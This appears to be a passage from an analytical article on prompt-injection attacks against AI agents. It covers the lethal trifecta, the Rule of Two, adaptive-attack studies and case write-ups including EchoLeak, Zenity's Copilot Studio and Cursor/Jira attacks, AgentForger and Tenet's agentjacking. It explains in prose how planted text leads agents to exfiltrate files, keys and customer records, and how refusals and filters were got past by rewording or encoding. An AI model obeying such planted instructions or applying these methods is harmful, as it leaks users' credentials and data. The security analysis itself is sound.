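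It is less clear whether planting a memory counts as a change of state under Meta's rule. In his notes on Meta's post, also titled *Agents Rule of Two* (2025), Bargury asked whether a change of state includes the agent's internal state. He guessed that it didn't, but thought it would have to as more agents keep notes between sessions. He also asked how a developer can distinguish spam, which is untrusted, from private email, which is sensitive, when both arrive in the same inbox. Developers would need to make that distinction to use Meta's option of reading only trusted senders.

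Willison (2025), in *New prompt injection papers*, welcomed the rule. He said the trifecta's one problem was that it covered only data theft, and that the rule solved this neatly by also counting changes of state. Soon afterwards he added a reservation, which he also posted to the forum Hacker News as simonw. Meta's diagram marked untrusted input plus the power to change state as "safe", but an agent with those two can do damage even without access to anything private. Making an exception for that pair would spoil the rule's simplicity.

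Human approval has since come to look like a weak fallback. In a study Anthropic published in August 2026, 1,053 paid testers worked with its coding agent, Claude Code, which asked their permission for certain actions. Partway through, the researchers replaced one request with a clearly dangerous command. Only 13.6 percent of the testers refused it. Anthropic was arguing for automatic checks, which it said would have blocked 89 percent of those commands. Willison still found the low refusal rate believable, because people who must click "OK" every few steps stop reading the requests.

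### How well newer models resist

Both the trifecta and the Rule of Two assume that attackers can still get models to follow planted instructions. If newer models ignored those instructions, developers could stop worrying about which capabilities they combine.

The main evidence against relying on this in 2025 came from *The Attacker Moves Second*, by Nasr, Carlini and colleagues, including researchers from OpenAI, Anthropic and Google DeepMind. They tested twelve published defences against prompt injection and jailbreaks. Three added wording to the prompt, three trained the model against known attacks, four used a separate filter, and two used a hidden test that the attacker isn't supposed to know about. The original papers for most of these defences reported that almost no attacks succeeded, usually in tests against a fixed collection of old attacks.

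Nasr and colleagues let the attacker adapt. In their search method, one model proposes several injections, the defended system processes them, and a second model scores how close each came to succeeding. The first model then uses the scores and the system's responses to revise the best attempts, for up to 800 tries. The team also used reinforcement learning, a contest with over 500 human participants, and a method based on gradients (calculations of how small changes to the text affect the output). For each defence, they picked the method they thought most likely to defeat it.

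They got past most of the defences more than 90 percent of the time. One defence repeats the user's request after the untrusted text, so that the model doesn't lose track of it. Old attacks succeeded against this defence as little as 1 percent of the time, but the search method succeeded more than 95 percent of the time. The best filter still let 71 percent of attacks through. At least one human attacker succeeded in each of the 29 scenarios that both people and the search attempted, while the search succeeded in 69 percent of them.

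GPT-5 Mini, one of the newer models, was tested with no added defence. It resisted all of the benchmark's stock attacks, but the search method succeeded in 75 percent of scenarios, typically after about 58 tries. Resistance to known attacks is therefore weak evidence that a model will resist an attacker who can test attacks beforehand, and anyone with an account can do that against a commercial assistant.

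Nasr and colleagues left out defences such as CaMeL, which plan the agent's actions from the user's request before it reads anything untrusted. They expected their attacks to fail against such defences in most of their scenarios, because planted text cannot alter the plan. These designs suit only some tasks, since an agent's next step often depends on what it reads.

Models have improved since then. *How Vulnerable Are AI Agents to Indirect Prompt Injections?* (Dziemian, Lin and colleagues, 2026) describes a contest run by the security company Gray Swan, in which 464 people made about 272,000 attempts against 13 models. To succeed, an injection usually had to cause a harmful action and keep any sign of it out of the agent's answer. The success rate ranged from 0.5 percent for Claude Opus 4.5 to 8.5 percent for Gemini 2.5 Pro. Participants could see the whole conversation before writing their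 attack, which real attackers rarely can.

A low success rate per attempt offers less protection when the attacker can try again. At 0.5 percent, an attacker has an even chance of succeeding at least once in 139 attempts, if the attempts are independent. In the contest, people broke Opus 4.5 in 13 of 37 scenarios. Successes continued at a roughly steady rate for every model, with no sign that attackers were running out of ideas. Gray Swan has repeated the contest into August 2026, according to the *Beam Model Technical Report* (2026).

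OpenAI then automated the attacker. In *GPT-Red*, Wallace, Choquette-Choo and colleagues (2026) trained an attacking model of the same name against a group of defending models. They rewarded the attacker for successful injections and the defenders for resisting and finishing their work, then used GPT-Red's attacks to train GPT-5.6. In a copy of Gray Swan's 2025 contest, GPT-Red succeeded in under 4 percent of attempts against GPT-5.6, without the other safeguards that surround the model in OpenAI's products. That result may overstate GPT-5.6's resistance, since it had trained on GPT-Red's attacks. GPT-5.6 also withstood all the human attacks saved from the contest. On the hardest material held back from training, its resistance rate ranged from just over 50 to 89 percent, and Wallace and colleagues call robustness "far from solved".

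Later figures vary with the test. Anthropic's June 2026 system card, the safety report published with a new model, gives Claude Mythos 5 the best result so far on a Gray Swan benchmark. Digital Applied (2026) quotes the card as giving a success rate of 0.41 percent for adaptive attacks on coding tasks, down from 2.09 percent for Claude Opus 4.8. In October, OpenAI reported that GPT-6 Sol resisted 97.13 percent of indirect injections and 99.99 percent of direct ones (Cross, 2026, *GPT-6 Sol Scores 97.13% on Indirect Injection Defense*). But *INFUSE* (2026), a benchmark published the same month, found that 19.6 percent of attacks succeeded on average across a range of models. PromptArmor's *FrontierBreach* reports successful attacks on leading models from every provider, including Gemini 4 Carbon, which no other known benchmark had broken.

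So Willison's "very good chance" no longer holds for the best models facing a stock attack. His point about filters has held up better, as a change to Claude Code in August 2026 showed. Anthropic made "auto mode", in which automatic checks replace most requests for permission, the default on most plans. It had commissioned Trajectory Labs to run 72 injection scenarios ten times each, and none of the 720 attempts succeeded against Claude Fable 5, Opus 5 or Sonnet 5. An Anthropic engineer joked that the announcement should have been called "defeating the lethal trifecta". Willison wrote that he would love to believe it but wanted more independent confirmation. He doubted that any such check could recognise a malicious package if a project's own instructions told the agent to run it.

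Rehberger published a successful attack on 26 August, less than two weeks after the change. A user asked Claude Code to summarise a web page, and the page led it to download an archive and run a harmless-looking program, which loaded a malicious file from the same archive. Willison (2026), in *Breaking Claude Code Opus 5 Auto Mode*, reports a claimed success rate of 80 percent and says that auto mode sometimes stopped Claude from halting the harmful code. Crosley, in *Claude Code Auto Mode Is Not a Security Boundary*, reports three successes in five runs for the main attack, and three in five and four in five for two versions of another. Five runs are too few for a reliable rate, but the successes show that the result of zero in 720 described those 72 scenarios and not what a skilled attacker could do. Anthropic had not publicly addressed the finding when The Next Web published *A researcher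 hijacked Claude Code*.

Hard boundaries fail too, but they can be repaired more completely. Claude's web tool blocks addresses that Claude has composed itself. In July 2026, Ayush Paul got around this with a website whose pages linked to one another letter by letter, and had Claude spell out a user's name, home city and employer by following the links. Anthropic stopped the tool from following links found on pages it had opened, which closed that route however the injection is worded.

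## What "zero-click" means when attacks arrive by email, ticket or MCP

Zenity called its attacks on ChatGPT, Copilot Studio, Cursor and Salesforce Einstein "0click". In its published ChatGPT attack, however, the victim uploads the attacker's document and asks for a summary, while the Copilot Studio attack runs with no user present. "Zero-click" can mean that the attacker's text gets in without any action by the victim, that stolen data gets out that way, or that even a careful victim could not have avoided the attack, and an attack may fit one of these meanings but not another.

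### Getting data out and getting text in

EchoLeak, the 2025 attack on Microsoft 365 Copilot, shows what "zero-click" means for data exfiltration. Ravia (2025), in *Breaking down 'EchoLeak'*, describes how Aim Labs, the research arm of Aim Security, removed the victim's actions one at a time. The researchers first had Copilot put a link in its answer, which the victim had to click. They then replaced the link with an image, which the browser loads automatically, but routing the image through SharePoint worked only if the victim had accepted an invitation to the attacker's site. Routing it through a Microsoft Teams service removed that requirement. *EchoLeak*, an academic case study of the attack, uses "zero-click" only for the version with the automatically loaded image. In that sense, the images that Samoilenko and Rehberger used in 2023 were also zero-click, even when the victim had to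 paste the attacker's text into ChatGPT.

Attacks differ in how much the victim must do before the assistant reads the attacker's text. A user may give the assistant the item containing it, as in the ChatGPT upload. A user may also ask an ordinary question, and the assistant finds the item while looking for an answer. In other cases, the item's arrival may start the agent with no user present.

EchoLeak requires an employee to use Copilot, but not to make a mistake. The attacker's email sits in the mailbox until the employee asks Copilot about something that seems related to it. Many retrieval systems represent each passage of text as a point in a mathematical space and fetch the passages closest to the question. A short email has only one point, so few questions would retrieve it. Aim Labs therefore wrote a long email that such a system would split into several passages, and repeated its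 instructions under headings on everyday office subjects. Ravia reports that Copilot then retrieved the email for questions on various topics, but gives no success rate.

Bargury classifies attacks by whether the victim has to make a mistake. In *Pwn the Enterprise*, a "1click" attack needs one ill-advised action, such as clicking a link, while a "0click" attack leaves the user with "nothing tangible they can do to protect themselves". Uploading a document to ChatGPT can count as zero-click under this definition if the document contains invisible instructions, because an ordinary user can't see them. Bargury labels the Gemini attack one-click because the victim, after asking about email or a supplier's bank details, makes the mistake of following a phishing link or paying the wrong account. However, the victim does less to get the attacker's text into Gemini than to get it into ChatGPT, which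 requires uploading the document.

Bargury also wrote that an attacker needed only a person's email address to take over that person's ChatGPT. The upload demonstration doesn't support that, since the attacker still has to get the victim to upload the file. The claim fits the shared-file version that The Decoder described in 2025, because an attacker needs only an email address to share a file. The victim must still ask a question that leads ChatGPT to the file.

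Zenity's *One Click, One Attacker-Controlled Agentic Insider* (2026) describes AgentForger, a flaw that allowed a one-click attack through the tool ChatGPT's business customers use to build agents. The tool accepted instructions in a link and ran them immediately. An attacker could therefore email an employee a link to the real ChatGPT site, and clicking it would make the employee's account build an agent.

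The Decoder's *One tampered ChatGPT link could spawn a rogue AI agent* reports that, after the click, the new agent gained access to accounts the employee had already connected, turned off requests for approval, and ran every five minutes. On each run it checked the employee's inbox for orders from the attacker, carried them out and emailed the results. In one test it found a database password in Slack and sent it to the attacker. Zenity reported the flaw on 4 June 2026, and OpenAI fixed it four days later by removing the part of the link that carried instructions.

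AgentForger resembles an older web attack, cross-site request forgery, in which a link makes a logged-in user's browser do something the user didn't intend. The attacker's text entered ChatGPT as the employee's own request rather than in a document or email the model was reading. Once the employee had clicked the link, the attacker could keep giving orders by email without the employee doing anything more, so the number of clicks an attack needs is a poor guide to how much damage it can do.

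### An email that starts the agent

Of the AgentFlayer attacks, the one on Copilot Studio best fits the term "zero-click". In October 2024, Microsoft released a video about an agent McKinsey had built to handle customer requests without staff taking part. When a customer wrote to a shared inbox, the agent looked up earlier work for that customer, chose a suitable consultant and emailed the consultant the details.

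Zenity Labs built a simplified copy that started whenever an email reached its inbox. The copy had a file matching customer accounts to support representatives, and tools for fetching Salesforce records and sending email. Its instructions were to read each request, find the right representative and pass the request on.

Sharbat began by finding out what the agent had access to. He sent it an email with instructions to report the names of its files to an outside address, and the agent replied with the name of the customer file. A slightly altered email made it list its tools, including an internal search tool that Copilot Studio agents use. Now that he knew what to ask for, Sharbat told the agent to send the contents of the file, and the whole file arrived seconds later. Another email told it to fetch customer records with the Salesforce tool, and it mailed back dozens of them, as many as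 would fit in one message.

Nobody at the company had to open an email, ask a question or approve anything. The attack didn't need a Markdown image either, because the agent could already send email to an outsider.

The demonstration exposed less data than some descriptions suggest. The stolen file had about ten rows, although Zenity Labs says an agent can leak about 100 at a time. In his summary, Bargury refers to the company's entire customer database, but the email shown in the write-up contained dozens of records. An attacker could presumably have requested more in further emails.

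Zenity's attack on a copy shows that a customer could build a dangerously exposed agent in Copilot Studio, but it doesn't show that an outsider could have stolen McKinsey's data. McKinsey's original agent drew on several databases, and Zenity wrote the copy's instructions and chose its connections. McKinsey may also have restricted what its agent could fetch or where it could send mail.

Microsoft's response is good evidence that the platform's weakness was real. Zenity reported it on 21 February 2025. Microsoft acknowledged the report a week later, confirmed the behaviour on 13 March and issued a fix on 24 April, which Zenity checked the next day. On 28 April, Microsoft awarded Zenity $8,000 and rated the flaw critical. The writer at Office 365 for IT Pros generally distrusts security researchers' reports because so many are overhyped, but took this one seriously because Microsoft had.

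Microsoft didn't explain the fix, but Zenity's tests suggested it was mainly a filter for injections. The original emails stopped working, but Sharbat, like Willison, expected reworded ones to get through.

He advised builders to list the exact addresses whose emails may start an agent. That would suit an internal agent, but a customer-service inbox has to accept mail from strangers. This agent's task was to alert colleagues, so restricting its outgoing mail to employees would fit better. It would also have kept the customer records from reaching Sharbat by email, however he worded his instructions.

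Bargury says Zenity used a tool called powerpwn to find more than 3,500 Copilot Studio agents on the internet. That figure doesn't measure how many were open to this theft, because an agent would also need to accept instructions from a stranger, have access to something worth stealing and be able to send it out.

### A support request that reaches a code editor

Simakov's attack on Cursor also starts with an email from a stranger, but a developer has to take part. Many companies use a helpdesk program such as Zendesk, which turns messages to a support address into tickets and copies them into Jira. According to Bargury, Zenity used Google searches to find hundreds of addresses that open Jira tickets automatically. An outsider's message to one of these addresses appears in the company's tracker among tickets written by employees.

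In this set-up, Cursor fetches the ticket through a Jira MCP server only when a developer asks for help with it, so the attack starts with the developer's request rather than with MCP. Until then, the malicious ticket can sit in Jira for weeks without any effect.

Zenity Labs' write-up describes two tests. In the first, Simakov's ticket asked openly for API keys stored in the project's code, and Cursor refused, citing good security practice. In the second, she replaced "API keys" with a harmless word, and Cursor found a login token in the code and sent it out. She used two routes to get stolen data out. Cursor could post a secret as a comment on the ticket, which a two-way link with Zendesk might pass back to the attacker, or put the secret in a web address and open that address.

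The first test relied on auto-run, which lets Cursor use its tools without asking permission each time. Simakov says this setting is common because approving every step is exhausting. Turning it off is a tangible step that gives the developer a chance to stop the theft, so the attack doesn't fit Bargury's definition of zero-click well. But it isn't a reliable defence, given how readily Anthropic's testers approved dangerous commands.

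In the second test, Simakov tried to steal credentials from outside the project. She put dummy keys for Amazon's cloud service in a folder elsewhere on her computer. Cursor rejected several attempts, so she encoded the instructions and presented them as part of a troubleshooting request. Cursor then searched her folders and found the keys. The External-File Protection setting was on, but it doesn't prevent Cursor from reading files outside the project.

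Cursor was ready to send the keys to an outside website, but nothing left the machine. Simakov described her set-up as having auto-run on, but she had it off at this point as a precaution, so Cursor waited for her approval. She wrote that with auto-run on, Cursor would have sent the keys without asking. The first test makes that likely, but the second showed only that Cursor would find the keys and prepare the request.

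Simakov reported the attack on 27 June 2025. Cursor replied three days later that this was a known issue, and that MCP servers connected to untrusted data "present a serious risk to users". It told users to review each server before installing it and to use only servers that access trusted content. That is hard with Jira, because one server delivers both colleagues' tickets and strangers' messages.

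Cursor also recommended .cursorignore, a list of files that its agent should not access, to protect secrets stored in a project. Simakov thinks the list is worth using but doesn't guarantee protection. Cursor's advice didn't address her second test, in which the keys were outside the project. Bargury lists the report as closed, without mentioning a fix.

### Earlier attacks and Ravia's criticism

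Two groups had published similar attacks through MCP before Simakov contacted Cursor. Invariant Labs' *GitHub MCP Exploited* (26 May 2025) is the original account of the GitHub attack that Willison described. Claude's desktop app asks for confirmation before each use of a tool, but Invariant Labs noted that many users choose "Always Allow" and stop watching. The attack therefore depended on the user making much the same choice as in Simakov's first test.

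The closer precedent came from the security company Cato Networks. Waizel, Attiya and Bamberger (2025) described it on 19 June in *Cato CTRL Threat Research*, as an attack through the MCP server of Atlassian, which makes Jira. An outsider submits a ticket containing malicious instructions through a company's support portal. When a support engineer uses an AI tool on the ticket, for example to summarise it, the tool follows those instructions with the engineer's permissions. It copies internal data into the ticket, where the outsider can read it.

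Simakov's attack got in the same way and used one of the same routes to get data out, but she targeted the developer's machine rather than data inside Jira. In her post, she credits Invariant Labs' work but doesn't mention Cato's. She reported the attack to Cursor only eight days after Cato published, so she may already have been working on it by then.

| Attack | Reported to vendor | Published | What sets it off |
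|---|---|---|---|
| EchoLeak | January 2025 | 11 June 2025 | An employee asks Copilot a related question |
| Copilot Studio | 21 February 2025 | 7 July 2025 | The email arrives |
| GitHub MCP | No date given | 26 May 2025 | The owner asks about open issues |
| Atlassian MCP | No date given | 19 June 2025 | A support engineer uses AI on the ticket |
| Cursor and Jira | 27 June 2025 | 1 August 2025 | A developer asks for help with the ticket |

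Itay Ravia, the head of Aim Labs, thought AgentFlayer added little to EchoLeak. Hackread's *AgentFlayer 0-click exploit abuses ChatGPT Connectors to Steal 3rd-party app data* quotes him as calling it "a subset of the same EchoLeak primitives". Primitives are the basic techniques that attackers combine into an attack. Aim and Zenity both sold protection for AI systems, so neither was a neutral judge of the other's research.

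Ravia is largely right about the ChatGPT attack, which is the subject of Hackread's article. That attack and EchoLeak both hide instructions in something the assistant reads, make it pick out private data, and send the data out through an image on a Microsoft domain that the assistant's defences allow. EchoLeak requires less of the victim than the published ChatGPT version, because nobody has to upload anything.

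The Copilot Studio attack fits the description much less well. EchoLeak needed a disguised link, a self-loading image and a relay because Microsoft 365 Copilot couldn't email the attacker. The agent Sharbat attacked could send email, so he needed none of them. He also made the agent query Salesforce with a tool he had discovered earlier, whereas EchoLeak took data that Copilot had already gathered in its conversation with the employee. Sharbat's email started the agent, while Aim's took effect only after the employee asked Copilot a question.

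The dates also make it unlikely that Zenity borrowed from EchoLeak. Aim Labs reported its attack to Microsoft about a month before Zenity did, but didn't publish it until June, after Microsoft had fixed both. If Ravia's description meant only that an outsider plants instructions where an assistant with private data will read them, it would cover the Copilot Studio attack. But then EchoLeak would itself be a subset of what Greshake and colleagues described in 2023.

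### Fake error reports in 2026

A year after Simakov's tests, the security company Tenet made coding agents run an attacker's program by a similar route. Tenet calls the technique "agentjacking" in *A Fake Bug Report Hijacks Your AI Coding Agent* (9 June 2026). The technique uses Sentry, a service that collects error reports from websites and apps. The key a website needs to send errors to Sentry is in the site's public code, where anyone can copy it.

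The attacker uses the key to submit a fake error containing what looks like Sentry's own advice for fixing it. When a developer asks a coding agent to deal with Sentry errors, the agent receives the report through Sentry's MCP server, treats the advice as genuine and runs the attacker's program with the developer's privileges. The program can then reach cloud keys, GitHub logins and the addresses of private code. Tenet's attacker needed only a public key, not a company that copied outside email into Jira, as Simakov's did.

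Tenet counted 2,388 organisations as exposed because they had usable keys, but some may not have connected a coding agent to Sentry. It says it saw more than 100 agents act on the planted errors in controlled testing, and it confirmed that agents had run its code at organisations ranging from a Fortune 500 company to independent developers. *New “Agentjacking” Attacks Could Hijack AI Coding Agents* (Muncaster, 2026) gives a success rate of 85 percent across popular agents, including Claude Code, Cursor and Codex, but not the number of attempts.

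Tenet says the attack needs "no user interaction beyond the developer's normal workflow", but the developer still has to ask about the errors, as in the GitHub attack. According to The Next Web's *Agentjacking*, agents ran the code even when their instructions told them to ignore untrusted data. Tenet told Sentry about the problem on 3 June. Sentry acknowledged it and added a filter for one specific piece of text, but declined to fix the cause, calling it "technically not defensible". In 2025, Cursor had said the risk came from the MCP servers. Sentry, which provides such a server, didn't accept that it could solve the problem at its end.

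Tenet extended the attack to other services in August, under the name "ghostjacking". Coker (2026), in *“Ghostjacking” Exploits AI Agents’ Trusted Access to Evade Firewall Controls*, describes a version that uses Cloudflare's website firewall. When the firewall blocks a malicious request, it copies the request word for word into a log. A company's analyst later asks an agent to review the blocked requests, and the agent reads the attacker's text. It then changes the company's DNS records, which direct web traffic and email to its servers, and reports the problem as solved. Tenet's attack succeeded nine times out of ten against Claude Code.

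Tenet's figures don't establish its claim that half of Fortune 500 companies are vulnerable. They show that 42 percent of those companies use Cloudflare and 48 percent use Datadog, a monitoring service that Tenet also attacked. But a company is exposed only if it also has an agent that reads the logs and has permission to act on them. Tenet recommends blocking agents' outgoing connections by default, which it says is enough to stop the attacker's download and the data leak. An agent that manages Cloudflare settings would need a connection to Cloudflare, so an attacker could still use it to redirect the company's email.
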